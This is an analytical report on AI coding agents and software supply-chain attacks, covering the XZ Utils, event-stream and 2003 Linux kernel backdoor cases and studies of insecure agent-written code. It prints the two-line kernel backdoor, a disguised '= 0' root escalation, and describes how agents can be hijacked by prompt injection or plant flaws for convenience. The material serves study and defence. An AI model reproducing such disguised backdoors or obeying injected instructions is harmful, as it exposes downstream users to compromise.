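# AI-proposed code changes that carry hidden vulnerabilities into the software supply chain

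## How a code change reaches users, and where a vulnerability can hide in it

Programmers rarely write a whole program themselves. They build on libraries and tools that other people maintain. Days or months after someone changes one of those parts, the change and any vulnerability it contains reach the machines of people who have never heard of it. A growing share of changes comes from coding agents, AI systems that read a code base, edit it and submit the result with little or no human help.

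An agent's code change goes through the same steps and checks as a human programmer's, and most projects designed those checks for human contributors. An agent can make a mistake that nobody notices, or a person can add a flaw on purpose by using an agent or tricking one. People were planting flaws in software long before coding agents existed. One of the clearest cases is a two-line change from more than twenty years ago.

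### From an edit to a release

Take an invented case. A library that reads image files crashes on a certain kind of picture, and a contributor wants to fix it.

The contributor copies the project's repository, which holds its source code and the history of every change, and edits the copy on their own machine. Nobody else checks the changes at this point. The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) guidance *Strategies for the Integration of Software Supply Chain Security in DevSecOps CI/CD* (Chandramouli, Kautz and Torres-Arias, 2024) treats the developer's machine as a risk in itself and recommends keeping it out of the build process.

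When the fix works, the contributor records it as a commit, which stores the edit with a name, a date and a short message. The name is whatever the contributor's software fills in, unless the project requires a cryptographic signature. The version control system (usually Git) produces a diff from the commit, which lists the lines added and removed, with a few unchanged lines around them for context. The contributor then opens a pull request, which proposes that the project accept the change. On many open-source projects, anyone can do this. Chandramouli and colleagues describe how an attacker can take the same route. The attacker copies the repository, modifies the copy and opens a pull request, and the change gets in if the maintainer (a person with authority to accept changes) merges it without reviewing it properly.

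Opening the pull request usually starts the build pipeline, the automated steps that test, build and publish the software. Developers call this stage continuous integration. According to *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026), the pipeline usually compiles the changed code and runs regression tests, which check that whatever worked before still works. If a job fails, the pipeline typically blocks the change. Some larger projects add fuzzing, running the program on very many automatically generated inputs to expose faulty behaviour, but often for only about ten minutes because developers need an answer quickly.

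None of this detects a hard-coded password or a hidden command line for an outsider, as Kokkonis and colleagues say plainly. Tests cover the behaviour that developers thought to test, and fuzzers look mainly for crashes and memory errors, which a backdoor need not cause. Projects can also run analysis tools over the source code to catch common mistakes. Chandramouli and colleagues recommend this, but caution that too many false alarms will wear developers out.

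Then someone reviews the diff. In a mature project the reviewer is a developer other than the author, and review is usually the only step at which anyone asks what the change is for. The reviewer has the changed lines and the contributor's explanation, and must get any other context from memory or by opening other files. If the reviewer is satisfied, a maintainer merges the change into the main code. Later contributors build on it, and under the usual process nobody has a reason to read it again.

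After the merge, the pipeline turns the source code into a form that a computer can run. Hardly anyone reads that output, so the project depends on build tools that nobody has tampered with. In *Linux kernel development process thwarts subversion attempt*, Miller and Barr recall a classic warning from Ken Thompson, a creator of Unix. He demonstrated in 1984 that an attacker could hide malicious code in a compiler, the tool that translates the source code, and that inspecting a program's own source would not reveal it.

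The maintainer then publishes a release, which is a package with a version number. Users have no guarantee that the package matches the code in the repository. Kokkonis and colleagues recount that in 2010 and 2011, attackers broke into the servers that distributed vsFTPd and ProFTPD, two file-transfer programs. For several days, those servers distributed packages with backdoors in them. Reviewing every pull request to the two projects would not have caught either attack, because the attackers did not submit their changes that way.

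Finally, the release reaches the programs that depend on it. A photo application picks up the new version of the image library, sometimes automatically, and Linux distributions such as Debian and Ubuntu package it for their own users. Distribution maintainers vet what they take in, but a release bundles many changes, and the diff between two releases can run from thousands to millions of lines. This last step attracts attackers because a compromised library can reach many other programs. The people who put a backdoor into the compression library XZ Utils in 2024 were targeting a remote-login program that depended on it.

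### Defect, backdoor or planted vulnerability

Together, these steps make up the software supply chain, which Chandramouli and colleagues define as a collection of steps that create, transform and assess software artifacts, meaning source code and whatever developers and tools produce from it. The actors who carry out the steps need not be human. The guidance gives an automated build system as its example, and a coding agent also fits the definition.

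A vulnerability is a weakness that someone could exploit. NIST's glossary entry for *vulnerability* collects more than a dozen definitions, most of them variations on a weakness that a threat source could "exploit or trigger". A few mention the intent of the person who later uses the weakness, but none depends on whether somebody put it there on purpose.

NIST defines a backdoor as an undocumented way of gaining access to a computer system. Kokkonis and colleagues use a narrower definition that is more useful for code changes. They define a backdoor as hidden functionality in the source code that gives extra privileges to anyone who knows a secret trigger. In the doctored vsFTPd, anyone who typed a smiley as a user name got a command line with full control of the machine.

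Malware is any software written to do harm, such as a program that steals passwords or encrypts files for ransom. A planted vulnerability is a defect that someone introduces on purpose and disguises as an ordinary mistake.

An investigator can sometimes establish intent from the code alone. A login routine that opens a root shell when someone enters a smiley, or a program that encrypts its owner's files and demands money, is clearly meant to do harm. A planted vulnerability always has a possible innocent explanation, because honest programmers make the same error all the time. Chandramouli and colleagues concede that the line between a defect and an attack is often blurred, and they draw it by whether the person upstream meant to exploit the flaw. That definition is reasonable but nearly useless for judging a diff, since a missing check looks the same whether its author forgot it or left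 it out deliberately. Investigators therefore need evidence of who submitted the change, from which account and by what route, and whether anyone went on to use the flaw.

### Two lines in the Linux kernel, 2003

In November 2003 somebody added two lines to a copy of the Linux kernel's source code. The kernel is the core of the operating system, and the lines went into the code for wait4, a function that a program calls to pause until another program has finished. McVoy (2003) posted the change in *BK2CVS problem*, a thread on the kernel developers' mailing list. Plus signs mark the new lines.

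```
+ if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
+         retval = -EINVAL;
  retval = -ECHILD;
```

On a quick read, this code appears to return the error code for an invalid argument if a program calls wait4 with a certain odd combination of options and the user ID is 0. System code is full of similar checks, and Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) says that even an expert reading casually would take this one for innocuous error-checking.

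The part before the `&&` is a real comparison. It is true only if the settings that the calling program passes in `options` are exactly the two flags `__WCLONE` and `__WALL`, which programs do not normally pass together. The `&&` means "and", and C evaluates what comes after it only if what comes before it is true. In everyday use, therefore, the new lines have no effect, and an ordinary regression test would pass.

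The trick is in the part after the `&&`. `current->uid` is the user ID of the running program. In C, `==` compares two values and a single `=` assigns one, so `current->uid = 0` sets the user ID to 0 instead of checking whether it is 0. On Linux, user ID 0 belongs to root, the account that may read, change or delete anything on the machine.

An assignment in C has a value, here 0, and C treats 0 as false. The whole condition therefore fails, `retval = -EINVAL` never runs, and no invalid-argument error comes back to suggest that anything unusual has happened. The calling program has full control from then on. By the definitions above, this is a backdoor, triggered secretly by a pair of flags. It is also a planted vulnerability, because its author disguised it as a typing error.

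A patient reader could have found two clues. Chad Kitching, a participant in McVoy's thread, noticed that the next line overwrites `retval`, so even a genuine version of the check would have had no effect. Another participant, Tomas Szepe, pointed to the parentheses around the assignment, which keep the compiler from warning about it. Neither clue is strong evidence of a deliberate vulnerability, though, because programmers do write useless checks, and many put parentheses around ordinary comparisons.

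The lines came to light through an automated check, not through anyone reading the code. The kernel's main repository was in a system called BitKeeper. For developers who disliked BitKeeper, McVoy's company BitMover also exported the code to a public copy in an older system, CVS. Every night a script compared checksums (short fingerprints of the files) between that public copy and BitMover's own. On 5 November one file did not match. McVoy looked at its history and found three extra entries under the name of a known kernel developer, who denied making them. Exported entries ended with a pointer to the corresponding change in BitKeeper, but these three had none, and the main repository contained no such change. Someone had apparently broken into the server and edited the public copy directly.

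Even then McVoy did not see what the lines did. He corrected the file and told the list that it was "not a big deal". Another developer asked, out of curiosity, what had changed. McVoy posted the lines, and 25 minutes later, according to the thread's time stamps, Kitching asked whether they were an attempt at a backdoor. Miller and Barr took the episode as a "stunning verification" of the open-source adage that many eyes make all bugs shallow. That seems generous, since the developers were quick only after an alarm had directed them to two lines already shown to be illegitimate. Torvalds, who leads kernel development, told Miller and Barr that the same change could be very hard to detect in the core repository of a project that really did use CVS, where it would be two lines among five million.

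When asked on the list whether the change could have reached a release, Torvalds said no. Changes got in either as patches emailed to him or through BitKeeper, and BitKeeper users would not have touched the CVS copy. McVoy was less sure, because a developer working from the CVS copy could have unknowingly included the two lines in a legitimate patch. *Thwarted Linux backdoor hints at smarter hacks* (Poulsen, 2003) also describes this path. Torvalds accepted emailed patches but said that core files "would definitely get a read-through". That safeguard depended on a busy reader spotting one missing equals sign, and McVoy's first look at the file suggests that a reader might have missed it. Debian's public vulnerability tracker lists the flaw, *CVE-2003-1161*, as one that local users could have exploited but that was never released.

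If it had gone that way, the flaw would have been much harder to explain. A reader commenting on *An attempt to backdoor the kernel* (2003), on the Linux news site LWN, pointed out that the next export would have overwritten the doctored copy, and the trail would have ended at the innocent developer who sent the patch. Security consultant Ryan Russell told Poulsen that the code was "indistinguishable from an accidental bug". Nobody has ever identified the culprit, and the evidence of malice is mostly circumstantial: the apparent break-in, the borrowed name and the missing record. McVoy also argued that only someone who knew the kernel well could have picked those flags, but a kernel developer who made a typing error would fit that description too.

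The check that worked in 2003 compared a copy with its original, so it could not catch a bad change that arrives by the proper route, with a plausible explanation and a record of approval. Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, raised that possibility in the same thread. He described a subtle patch that claims to fix a bug but opens a security hole, submitted among several other plausible changes.

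### Four ways an agent's change can come to be vulnerable

A coding agent's pull request normally arrives through the project's proper route for submitting changes. It could still contain a vulnerability as small as a single equals sign where there should be two.

- **Honest mistake:** the agent wrote faulty code, as human programmers do, and nobody intended the flaw.
- **Malicious operator:** the person running the agent told it to write the flaw and to make it look like a slip.
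- **Hijacked or poisoned agent:** an outsider steered the agent, either by placing instructions in text that it reads while working or by tampering with the data that its developers trained it on.
- **Illegitimate means:** nobody asked for the flaw, and the agent introduced it because extra access, or one check fewer, helped it to complete the task it had.

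## Malicious commits planted by people

There is a fairly good public record of how people have planted flaws in software. Such an attack has five stages. First, the attacker gains some right to contribute by opening an account, earning a maintainer's trust or stealing someone else's access. Second, the attacker writes a change that appears to have an innocent purpose. Third, someone with authority must accept the change, unless the attacker already has that authority. Fourth, the change must get into a release, because until then it reaches few people besides the project's own developers. Fifth, it must stay unnoticed long enough for the attacker to use it.

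Success at one stage can make another unnecessary or impossible. The 2003 intruder avoided the kernel's reviewers by editing a copy of the code, but Torvalds did not make releases from that copy.

Other researchers divide the stages differently. *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains* (2025) divides the XZ Utils attack into three: legitimate contributions, escalation of control and deployment of the backdoor. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (Lins, Mayrhofer and colleagues, 2024) matches possible defences to each stage of the same attack. Treating acceptance and release as separate stages is useful for XZ because part of the backdoor never went through the repository.

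### XZ Utils, 2021 to 2024

XZ Utils is a set of compression tools, and many Linux programs rely on its library, liblzma. Lasse Collin had designed the file format with others between 2005 and 2008, and in 2021 he was still maintaining the project without pay. That October, someone using the name Jia Tan sent a small, harmless patch to its mailing list, followed by others. Russ Cox (2024) reconstructed the attack from emails and commits in *Timeline of the xz open source attack*, and considers these early patches fine even in retrospect. Jia Tan eventually wrote more than 500 patches across several projects, so anyone who checked the name would have found an active and competent programmer.

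The pressure on Collin began in April 2022. Someone posting as "Jigar Kumar" complained that Collin had not merged one of Jia Tan's patches, though he had already merged four others. Someone posting as "Dennis Ens" asked whether anyone still maintained the Java version. Collin apologised for being slow and suggested that Jia Tan might take on a bigger role. In June, Kumar wrote that there would be no progress without a new maintainer. Collin answered that long-term mental health problems had limited his work, and reminded the list that this was "an unpaid hobby project". Ens said he was sorry to hear it and proposed that Collin hand the project over. By the end of the month, Collin was calling Jia Tan "practically a co-maintainer already".

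The journalist Brian Krebs noticed that many of the complainers' email addresses appear nowhere else on the internet, even in leaked data. Cox thinks somebody probably invented these people to push Collin into giving up control. At the time, they would have been hard to tell from ordinary impatient users on the mailing list.

Jia Tan was merging commits directly by December 2022 and published a first release in March 2023. That month, Jia Tan also changed the settings of OSS-Fuzz, Google's free fuzzing service for open-source projects, to receive its bug reports on XZ. In June another newcomer, "Hans Jansen", contributed a change that made the library choose its fastest checksum routine at start-up. The backdoor later used this change as its entry point. Collin, an honest maintainer, read the change closely and reworked it before it was merged, but he had little reason to object because by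 itself it could have been an innocent speed improvement.

The backdoor arrived in two parts. On 23 February 2024, Jia Tan merged most of it into the repository, hidden in binary files that looked like test files. Testing a compression library requires strange and damaged files, and the project's documentation had long explained that many of them were made by hand and had no more readable source. A diff is almost useless for such files. The one clue was that no test in that version used the new files, as Freund (2024) later pointed out in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*.

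The next day Jia Tan published version 5.6.0. The downloadable package contained an altered build script that was not in the repository. When a Linux distribution built its own package from the download, the script extracted the hidden code and put it into the library. Neither the script nor the hidden code did anything without the other. Someone comparing the package with the repository would have found the extra script, but release packages normally contain generated scripts that the repository lacks, so the script was not suspicious in itself. *xz backdoor*, by Collin (Larhzu), confirms that Jia Tan created and signed the packages for both bad versions. The signatures were genuine, so checking them would not have revealed the tampering. "Provenance, identity and permissions" covers how far signed and reproducible releases help.

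The target was OpenSSH, the program administrators use to log in to servers remotely. OpenSSH does not use liblzma itself, but Debian and several other distributions had modified it to work with systemd, the software that starts and supervises programs on most Linux machines. The modified version loaded systemd's library, which depended on liblzma. On an affected server, the attacker could run commands without logging in.

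Four days after the release, another change, which reviewers could read in full, added a typo to a test in the build. The test checks whether Landlock, a Linux security feature, is available, and the typo made it always fail. The commit record lists Collin as the person who accepted the change. Cox thinks Collin probably missed the typo, though Jia Tan may have forged the entry. The change resembles a smaller version of the 2003 kernel attempt, and it suggests that a one-character error can still get past someone who knows the code well.

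In early March, users of Red Hat's distributions began seeing errors at the entry to the backdoor from Valgrind, a tool that checks how programs use memory. Jia Tan committed a supposed fix as a distraction, then quietly changed the hidden files and released 5.6.1. Around the same time, the systemd developers accepted a change that would apparently have defeated the attack once distributions adopted it. They were trying to reduce dependencies for unrelated reasons. Hans Jansen reappeared on 25 March to ask Debian to adopt the new version, and Debian did so two days later.

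Andres Freund, a software developer, had meanwhile noticed that remote logins on his Debian test installations were using a lot of processor time. He found that a login that was bound to fail took about 0.3 seconds normally and 0.8 seconds with the new library, because the backdoor searched memory for the functions it needed. He first assumed that someone had tampered with Debian's package, then traced the problem to XZ itself. He reported it privately on 28 March and publicly the next day, noting that he was not a security researcher.

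By then the attacker had spent nearly 28 months preparing, and the backdoor had been in the repository for 34 days. Most of the affected distributions had included it only in pre-release versions. Freund thought it unlikely that someone had taken over an innocent maintainer's computer, because the maintainer had discussed the false "fixes" on several mailing lists. As in 2003, the evidence of intent came largely from what the attacker did outside the code.

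### PHP and event-stream

Jia Tan took more than a year to earn the right to change the code directly, whereas the people who attacked PHP, a programming language used by many websites, gained that ability in 2021 by breaching the project's Git server. They then added commits under the names of known PHP developers. According to Kokkonis and colleagues, the commits put a backdoor into PHP's built-in web server that let an outsider run code by sending a specially written request. The project's developers caught the backdoor before an official release.

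Breaking in is much quicker than earning commit access, but it is harder to hide, because the person whose name the attacker uses can read the history and see a commit they didn't make. The attacker behind the xz backdoor committed from their own account, under the name Jia Tan, and answered other developers' questions about those commits.

The handover of event-stream in 2018 was closer to XZ, but it needed no pressure campaign. Event-stream was a small JavaScript package that many other packages relied on. Its maintainer had stopped using it, and he gave a stranger who offered to take over the right to publish new versions. The new maintainer did some ordinary work, then made event-stream depend on another package, flatmap-stream. A later version of flatmap-stream contained encrypted code for stealing from users of one particular bitcoin wallet.

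A reviewer of event-stream's own code would have seen a new dependency but nothing malicious, because the harmful code was inside that dependency. The harmful code went unnoticed for more than a month, until developers looked into a warning about an outdated function that it happened to call.

### The "hypocrite commits" affair

In August 2020, researchers at the University of Minnesota tested the Linux kernel's review process by sending its developers deliberately flawed patches under false identities. Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu described the work in a paper on "hypocrite commits", due to appear at a leading security conference in 2021. In April 2021, more poor patches arrived from the university. Greg Kroah-Hartman, who maintains the kernel's stable releases, thought they were part of the same experiment and banned the university from contributing. The Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory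 Board then organised a review of all previously accepted patches from people at the university.

The board went through 435 commits. Tom's Hardware's *Linux Foundation Issues Frosty Final Judgment in UMN Scandal* gives the breakdown from board member Kees Cook's email:

- 349 were correct.
- 39 were incorrect and still needed fixing.
- 25 had already received fixes in later commits.
- 12 no longer mattered.
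- 9 dated from before the research group existed.
- 1 came out at its author's request.

TechRadar's *Linux review board says rogue researchers did not successfully insert buggy patches* quotes the board's report, which said that kernel developers had "caught, or ignored" every deliberately flawed patch and that the review process had "worked as intended".

That is a generous reading. Ignoring a patch keeps it out of the kernel, but it does not mean that anyone noticed the flaw. The experiment was also tiny. The University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) puts it at four patches, one of them valid, which leaves three chances to catch something. (The board's timeline, as Cook (2021), in *Re: Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident*, reproduces it, lists five messages and starts five days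 earlier.)

The audit also found 39 commits that needed fixing and 25 that had already received fixes. Kernel developers had therefore accepted 64 faulty changes, about 15% of the total. The university maintains that its researchers submitted all of them in good faith. Not every faulty patch is a vulnerability, but if reviewers let through that many honest mistakes, they probably would not reliably stop a deliberate one that looked the same.

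Developers also made the opposite error, treating honest patches as malicious. The April 2021 patches that led to the ban were, by the university's account, unnecessary and poor in quality but submitted in good faith. Cook later agreed that a message calling the university's commits "bad faith" should have distinguished intentional flaws from unintentional ones. These episodes suggest that developers, who could not see intent, were reacting to the quality of a patch and the reputation of its sender.

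The strongest criticism of the study concerned consent. Wheeler (2021), in *Re: Malicious commits to Linux kernel as part of university study*, objected that the researchers had experimented on people without asking them and had gone to their university's ethics board only afterwards. In the comments under LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021), one of four researchers who had complained to the conference's chairs argued that wasted time counts as harm and that deliberate deception makes the lack of consent worse. Another commenter disagreed, finding it absurd to compare a bad patch to a medical experiment, and likened the study to the fake phishing emails that companies send to their own staff. The usual answer is that someone in charge has authorised a phishing test, whereas nobody in charge of the kernel had authorised the study.

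Lu, Wu and their colleague Aditya Pakki replied in *An open letter to the Linux community* (University of Minnesota, 2021). They apologised and explained that they had not asked permission because the maintainers would then have been on the lookout. They insisted that the three incorrect patches never got beyond discussion on a mailing list, and that their other patches had nothing to do with the study. Two days later Wu and Lu (2021) withdrew the paper, writing that they did not want to benefit from an improperly conducted study or have others copy its method. They now recommended getting approval from a project's leaders beforehand.

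The researchers' worry about forewarning reviewers was legitimate, but getting advance approval from a few leaders and leaving the reviewers themselves uninformed would have partly addressed it. The clean-up took a lot of work. TechRadar's *More than 80 Linux devs called on to help to fix 'mess'* reports that more than 80 developers took part in the re-review. The board advised the university to have an experienced developer check its patches before submitting more.

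### How often diff review did the catching

| Case | Entry | Concealment | Time undetected | How found |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Linux kernel, 2003 | Apparent break-in at a server holding a copy | Two lines resembling an error check | Probably a day at most | Automated comparison with the original |
| event-stream, 2018 | Handover by a maintainer who had moved on | Encrypted code in a new dependency | More than a month | Developers followed up a warning |
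| Hypocrite commits, 2020 | Emailed patches under false names | Flaws in ordinary-looking patches | Never merged | Reviewers caught or ignored them |
| PHP, 2021 | Breached Git server | Names of known developers | Too short to reach a release | Manual inspection after the commits were in |
| XZ Utils, 2024 | Maintainer role earned in a little over a year | Backdoor split between test files and release package | 34 days | Slow logins |

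Reviewing a proposed diff stopped only one of these five attacks, and that one was an experiment. The PHP case is partial evidence that human review works, but the reviewers were reading changes already in the repository. Luck played a large part in the other cases. If the XZ backdoor had run faster, it might have lasted for months.

These four cases mostly show attackers avoiding an independent reviewer, rather than reviewers missing malicious code. The intruders at the kernel's copy server and at PHP bypassed review, and the new maintainers of event-stream and XZ could approve their own work. Only the Minnesota patches, Jansen's speed improvement and perhaps the Landlock typo tested a reviewer, which is far too few cases to estimate a detection rate.

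The table also leaves out undiscovered attacks. If a planted vulnerability looks like an ordinary bug, someone may eventually fix it without asking where it came from. A commenter on LWN's article made a similar point about the Minnesota patches, saying that a real attacker would not have published a paper afterwards.

### What practitioners said in 2024

Six months after the XZ backdoor was discovered, three academic researchers spent a day discussing supply-chain security with 12 practitioners from nine companies. The rules allowed the researchers to report what people said but not who said it. *S3C2 Summit 2024-09* (Rahman, Acar and colleagues, 2025) reports that everyone considered malicious commits hard to detect and nobody could name a good solution.

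One participant compared the task to the halting problem. No procedure can correctly tell, for every possible program, whether it will eventually stop. Suppose someone adds an instruction to any harmless program that opens a backdoor once the program has finished. The combined program opens the backdoor only if the original one stops. A perfect backdoor detector would therefore also solve the halting problem, so no such detector can exist.

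The comparison is correct, but it rules out only a tool that is right about every program. A tool could still catch most backdoors while raising some false alarms and sometimes giving no answer, and "Static analysis, fuzzing and comparison of behaviour" covers several attempts to build one. The comparison also leaves out intent, which even complete knowledge of a program's behaviour would not always reveal.

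In practice, the participants relied on partial signals. One suggested banning binary files from repositories. That would have blocked the hidden files in XZ, though a compression project has a stronger case than most for an exception. Another suggested requiring several people to approve each change, but many open-source packages have only one or two active maintainers, and one of XZ's two was the attacker.

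Reputation is no more dependable, because Jia Tan had a good one, honest newcomers have none, and attackers can take over a trustworthy person's account. Some participants preferred to limit the damage by giving each package only the permissions it needs or by running it in isolation. Isolation works poorly for languages that let a program create and execute new code while running.

That left human review as the usual fallback, but the participants did not think it reliable either. They described commits that look harmless individually and become malicious only in combination with others, as Jansen's change to XZ did. They also stressed that analysing commits is not enough on its own. An attack on the build system, like the one on SolarWinds disclosed in 2020, may leave no suspicious commit to analyse. Other proposals dealt with paying the maintainers of critical projects and with burnout,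 which in Collin's case had given the attacker an opening almost two years before the first malicious commit.

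## How a vulnerability gets into an agent's change

The attackers in these cases had to earn the right to contribute, steal it or talk someone into granting it. A coding agent usually has that right already, so an attacker only has to influence what it writes. Often, though, the flaw is accidental, because agents make mistakes as people do. The more often they make them, the harder it is to spot a flaw that somebody planted.

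### Honest mistakes in real projects

Most of the field evidence comes from AIDev, a public dataset of pull requests that coding agents submitted on GitHub. Its curated subset contains 33,596 pull requests to 2,807 fairly popular repositories, submitted by five agents: OpenAI Codex, GitHub Copilot, Devin, Cursor and Claude Code. Codex submitted 21,799 of them. The data end in the summer of 2025, so they describe agents that are now more than a year old.

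In *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests*, Rabbi, Turzo and colleagues (2026) found 675 pull requests that dealt with security by searching for keywords and having a language model discard the false matches. They ran Semgrep, a tool that looks for code patterns typical of vulnerabilities, on each project before and after the change, and kept only the new alerts. At least one new alert appeared in 104 of the 675 (15.4%), although most of these changes were supposed to make the software safer.

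| Weakness | What goes wrong | New alerts |
|---|---|---|
| Inefficient regular expression | A crafted input keeps a text-matching pattern busy for a very long time | 306 |
| Command injection | Outside input ends up in a command that the operating system runs | 110 |
| Path traversal | A crafted file name reaches files outside the intended folder | 87 |
| Uncontrolled format string | Outside input serves as the template for a program's output | 69 |
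| Cross-site scripting | Outside input runs as code in another visitor's browser | 60 |
| Hard-coded credentials | A password or key sits in the source code | 48 |

In Rabbi and colleagues' data, 289 of the 306 alerts for inefficient regular expressions came from at most 15 pull requests, all from Copilot and all rejected. This makes their conclusion that agents often write such expressions doubtful. The same pull requests produced 92 of the command-injection alerts and 40 of those for hard-coded credentials. Path traversal is more widespread. At least 57 of its 87 alerts were in changes that maintainers merged, and those changes came from Copilot, Devin and Codex.

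The breakdown also implies that maintainers merged 51 of the 104 pull requests with new alerts. Alerts appeared in 14.4% of the merged changes and 13.2% of the rejected ones, so an alert seems to have made almost no difference to whether a change was merged. Semgrep raises false alarms, and some maintainers may have checked the code and rightly judged it safe. The reasons for rejection suggest that security was seldom the issue. Nobody gave a reason for 38.8% of the 219 rejected pull requests, and another 12.3% closed after a period of inactivity. Maintainers turned down 10.5% for introducing bugs or breaking compatibility, 5.9% for poor design, 4.1% for failing or missing tests and 3.7% for style. None of the 14 categories of rejection reasons is specifically for adding a vulnerability, although the one for bugs may include some.

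Siddiq, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Security in the Age of AI Teammates*, searched the same 33,596 pull requests with different keywords and checked the matches by hand. They counted 1,293 as security-related, nearly twice as many, which shows how loosely that category is defined. They compared the outcomes of pull requests but did not look for new flaws. Maintainers merged 61.5% of the agents' security-related pull requests that had reached a decision, compared with 77.3% of the agents' other pull requests and 79.2% of people's security-related ones in the same repositories.

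Much of the gap in merge rates between agents' security-related changes and their other changes comes from size rather than from reviewers taking special care with security work. When Siddiq and colleagues grouped the pull requests by the length of their descriptions, maintainers merged the two kinds equally often in the short and medium groups. In the longest group, they merged 53.4% of the security-related changes and 60.2% of the others. The rejected security-related changes were also larger, averaging about 2,720 changed lines against 1,873 for the merged ones. The section "What human reviewers catch" covers how size affects a reviewer's attention.

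Neither study shows whether agents make more of these mistakes than people do. *Not All Agents Are Equal* (Kraishan, 2026) compares agents' changes with 4,027 human pull requests from the same months, in repositories that also received agents' changes. In the 8,933 pull requests with Python, JavaScript or TypeScript code, Kraishan searched the added lines for text patterns of eight kinds of weakness, such as hard-coded passwords and database queries built by joining pieces of text. At least one pattern appeared in 2.9% of the agents' changes and 4.6% of the human ones.

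The agents' rates ranged from 1.6% for Cursor to 9.5% for Claude Code. Claude Code's changes had a median of 495 changed lines, against 52 for people, so its rate is a poor measure of how careful it was per line. A search for fixed patterns misses any flaw that depends on context, which is probably one reason these rates are so much lower than the 15.4% that Rabbi and colleagues found with Semgrep. Still, on this evidence, the agents of 2025 were no more careless than the people working beside them, at least about mistakes that a text search can find.

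### How often working code is insecure

Running an attack against the code is a much better test than searching it for patterns. *Last Secure Code Benchmark* (Wu, Ge and colleagues, 2026) cut the vulnerable code out of projects with 150 real vulnerabilities and asked an agent to write a replacement from a description of what the code should do, with no mention of security. Each vulnerability yielded three tasks: replacing a function, a whole file or a large part of the program. Hidden tests checked whether the new code worked, and also replayed the attack against it.

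The six agents tested produced working code for 73.6% to 91.3% of the 450 tasks, but they produced code that both worked and withstood the attack for only 16.4% to 25.1%. Claude Fable 5 had the highest rate on this second measure, at 25.1%.

In one task, the agent had to write a service that imports files in YAML, a common format for structured data. Kimi K3 wrote and tested the service and fixed a problem with corrupt files. Its code passed all 14 functional tests but failed all four security tests, because it used the YAML library's default reader, which creates program components specified by tags in an uploaded file. Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol used the library's safe reader and passed both sets of tests. The two versions behave identically on ordinary files, so a regression test would not detect the difference.

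Results also depended on the kind of weakness. Across all six agents, 34.3% of attempts succeeded on both counts when the risk was a memory error, such as writing past the end of a buffer, compared with 0.7% when the code had to withhold sensitive information. Wu and colleagues explain that a bounds check is part of writing the function well, whereas nothing in the surrounding code shows which data an outsider may see. The agent would have to think about how people will use and attack the program, and the instructions did not ask it to.

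When the team added one sentence telling the agent to make the code secure, the share of tasks with working and secure code rose by 15 to 21 percentage points for three of the four models they retested. The fourth, DeepSeek V4 Pro, barely improved. GPT-5.6 Sol did best, producing working and secure code on 46.2% of tasks, but nearly half of its working solutions were still open to the attack.

The benchmark shows that when a task makes it easy to introduce a vulnerability, today's agents usually do so while delivering code that works. These figures do not mean that three quarters of all the code agents write is vulnerable, because the selection of tasks favoured complicated cases. Every task also comes from a place where the original programmers had already made a mistake, so the original human code would score zero by the same measure.

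Results on SusVibes, an older set of 186 Python tasks, give some idea of the trend. In *Is Vibe Coding Safe?* (2025), the best agent, SWE-agent with Claude 4 Sonnet, solved 57% of the tasks, but 79.3% of those solutions were insecure, so about 12% of all its attempts were both correct and secure. *Secure Agentic Coding through Counterexample-Grounded Feedback* (2026) reports that by October 2026 a different agent, OpenCode with GPT-5.4, passed the functional tests on 93.01% of the tasks and the security tests on 28.49%. Both scores had improved, but only working code had become close to routine.

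Some of these mistakes reach users. Georgia Tech SSLab's *Vibe Security Radar* lists 78 published vulnerabilities, from May 2025 to 24 March 2026, that its researchers attribute to AI-written code. One is in OpenClaw, an open-source AI assistant, and the radar links it to Claude Code. OpenClaw checked its list of permitted users against display names, which people choose for themselves, so anyone could get past the check by taking a name on the list. Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Researchers Sound the Alarm on Vulnerabilities in AI-Generated Code* reports monthly counts of six in January 2026, 15 in February and at least 35 in March.

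That rise could mean that agents' code is getting worse, that there is much more of it, or that more people are looking for flaws. The site carries a warning about errors and omissions, and it uses a language model to verify its entries. Only 24% of the 46,831 security advisories it scanned to find the 78 included a fix. Without one, it is hard to trace a flaw to the change that introduced it, so the true number could be much higher.

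### Why honest flaws give planted ones cover

When honest mistakes are more common, a flaw is weaker evidence that its author meant harm. Suppose that agents send a project 10,000 pull requests, that attackers have planted a flaw in 10 of them, and that 15% of the rest contain an honest flaw. The 15% is close to the alert rate that Rabbi and colleagues measured, and the other figures are invented. A reviewer who caught every flaw would find about 1,500 flawed changes, of which one in 150 would be malicious. If agents made honest mistakes in only 1% of their changes, the reviewer would find about 110, of which one in 11 would be malicious.

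Investigating 110 contributors would be tedious but possible. With 1,500, the only practical response is to fix each flaw without investigating further, which leaves the attacker free to try again.

Agents may make suspicious patterns of changes harder to notice, as well as single flaws. In 2021, a batch of poor patches made Linux kernel maintainer Greg Kroah-Hartman suspect the University of Minnesota, but a similar batch from a coding agent would surprise hardly anyone. A person who tells an agent to write a vulnerability could also plausibly blame the model if somebody finds it.

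Better agents would therefore leave fewer accidental vulnerabilities for attackers to find and make deliberate ones stand out more. The same reasoning applies when an agent introduces a flaw for its own convenience, with no attacker involved. "An agent that tried to get malicious code merged, compared with human attackers" covers that case.

### Text that redirects an agent

An attacker who does not run a coding agent can still try to steer it through prompt injection, which means putting a command in text that the agent will read. The agent receives its user's request, the project's files and the output of its tools as text, and its language model cannot reliably separate instructions from material it should only read. The model may therefore follow the attacker's command. Coding agents are unusually exposed to prompt injection because most of their work is reading text that other people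 wrote.

Issues are the easiest place to put such text. An issue is a bug report or request on a project's public page, and on many open-source projects anyone can write one. Usually, a maintainer assigns Copilot an issue and it opens a pull request in response. Siddiq and colleagues found that 81.2% of Copilot's security-related pull requests were linked to an existing issue. This shows how often an agent's work begins with text that a stranger could have written, though it isn't evidence of any attack. Where an agent runs inside the build pipeline, injected text may do harm without any pull request (see "Changes to the build pipeline").

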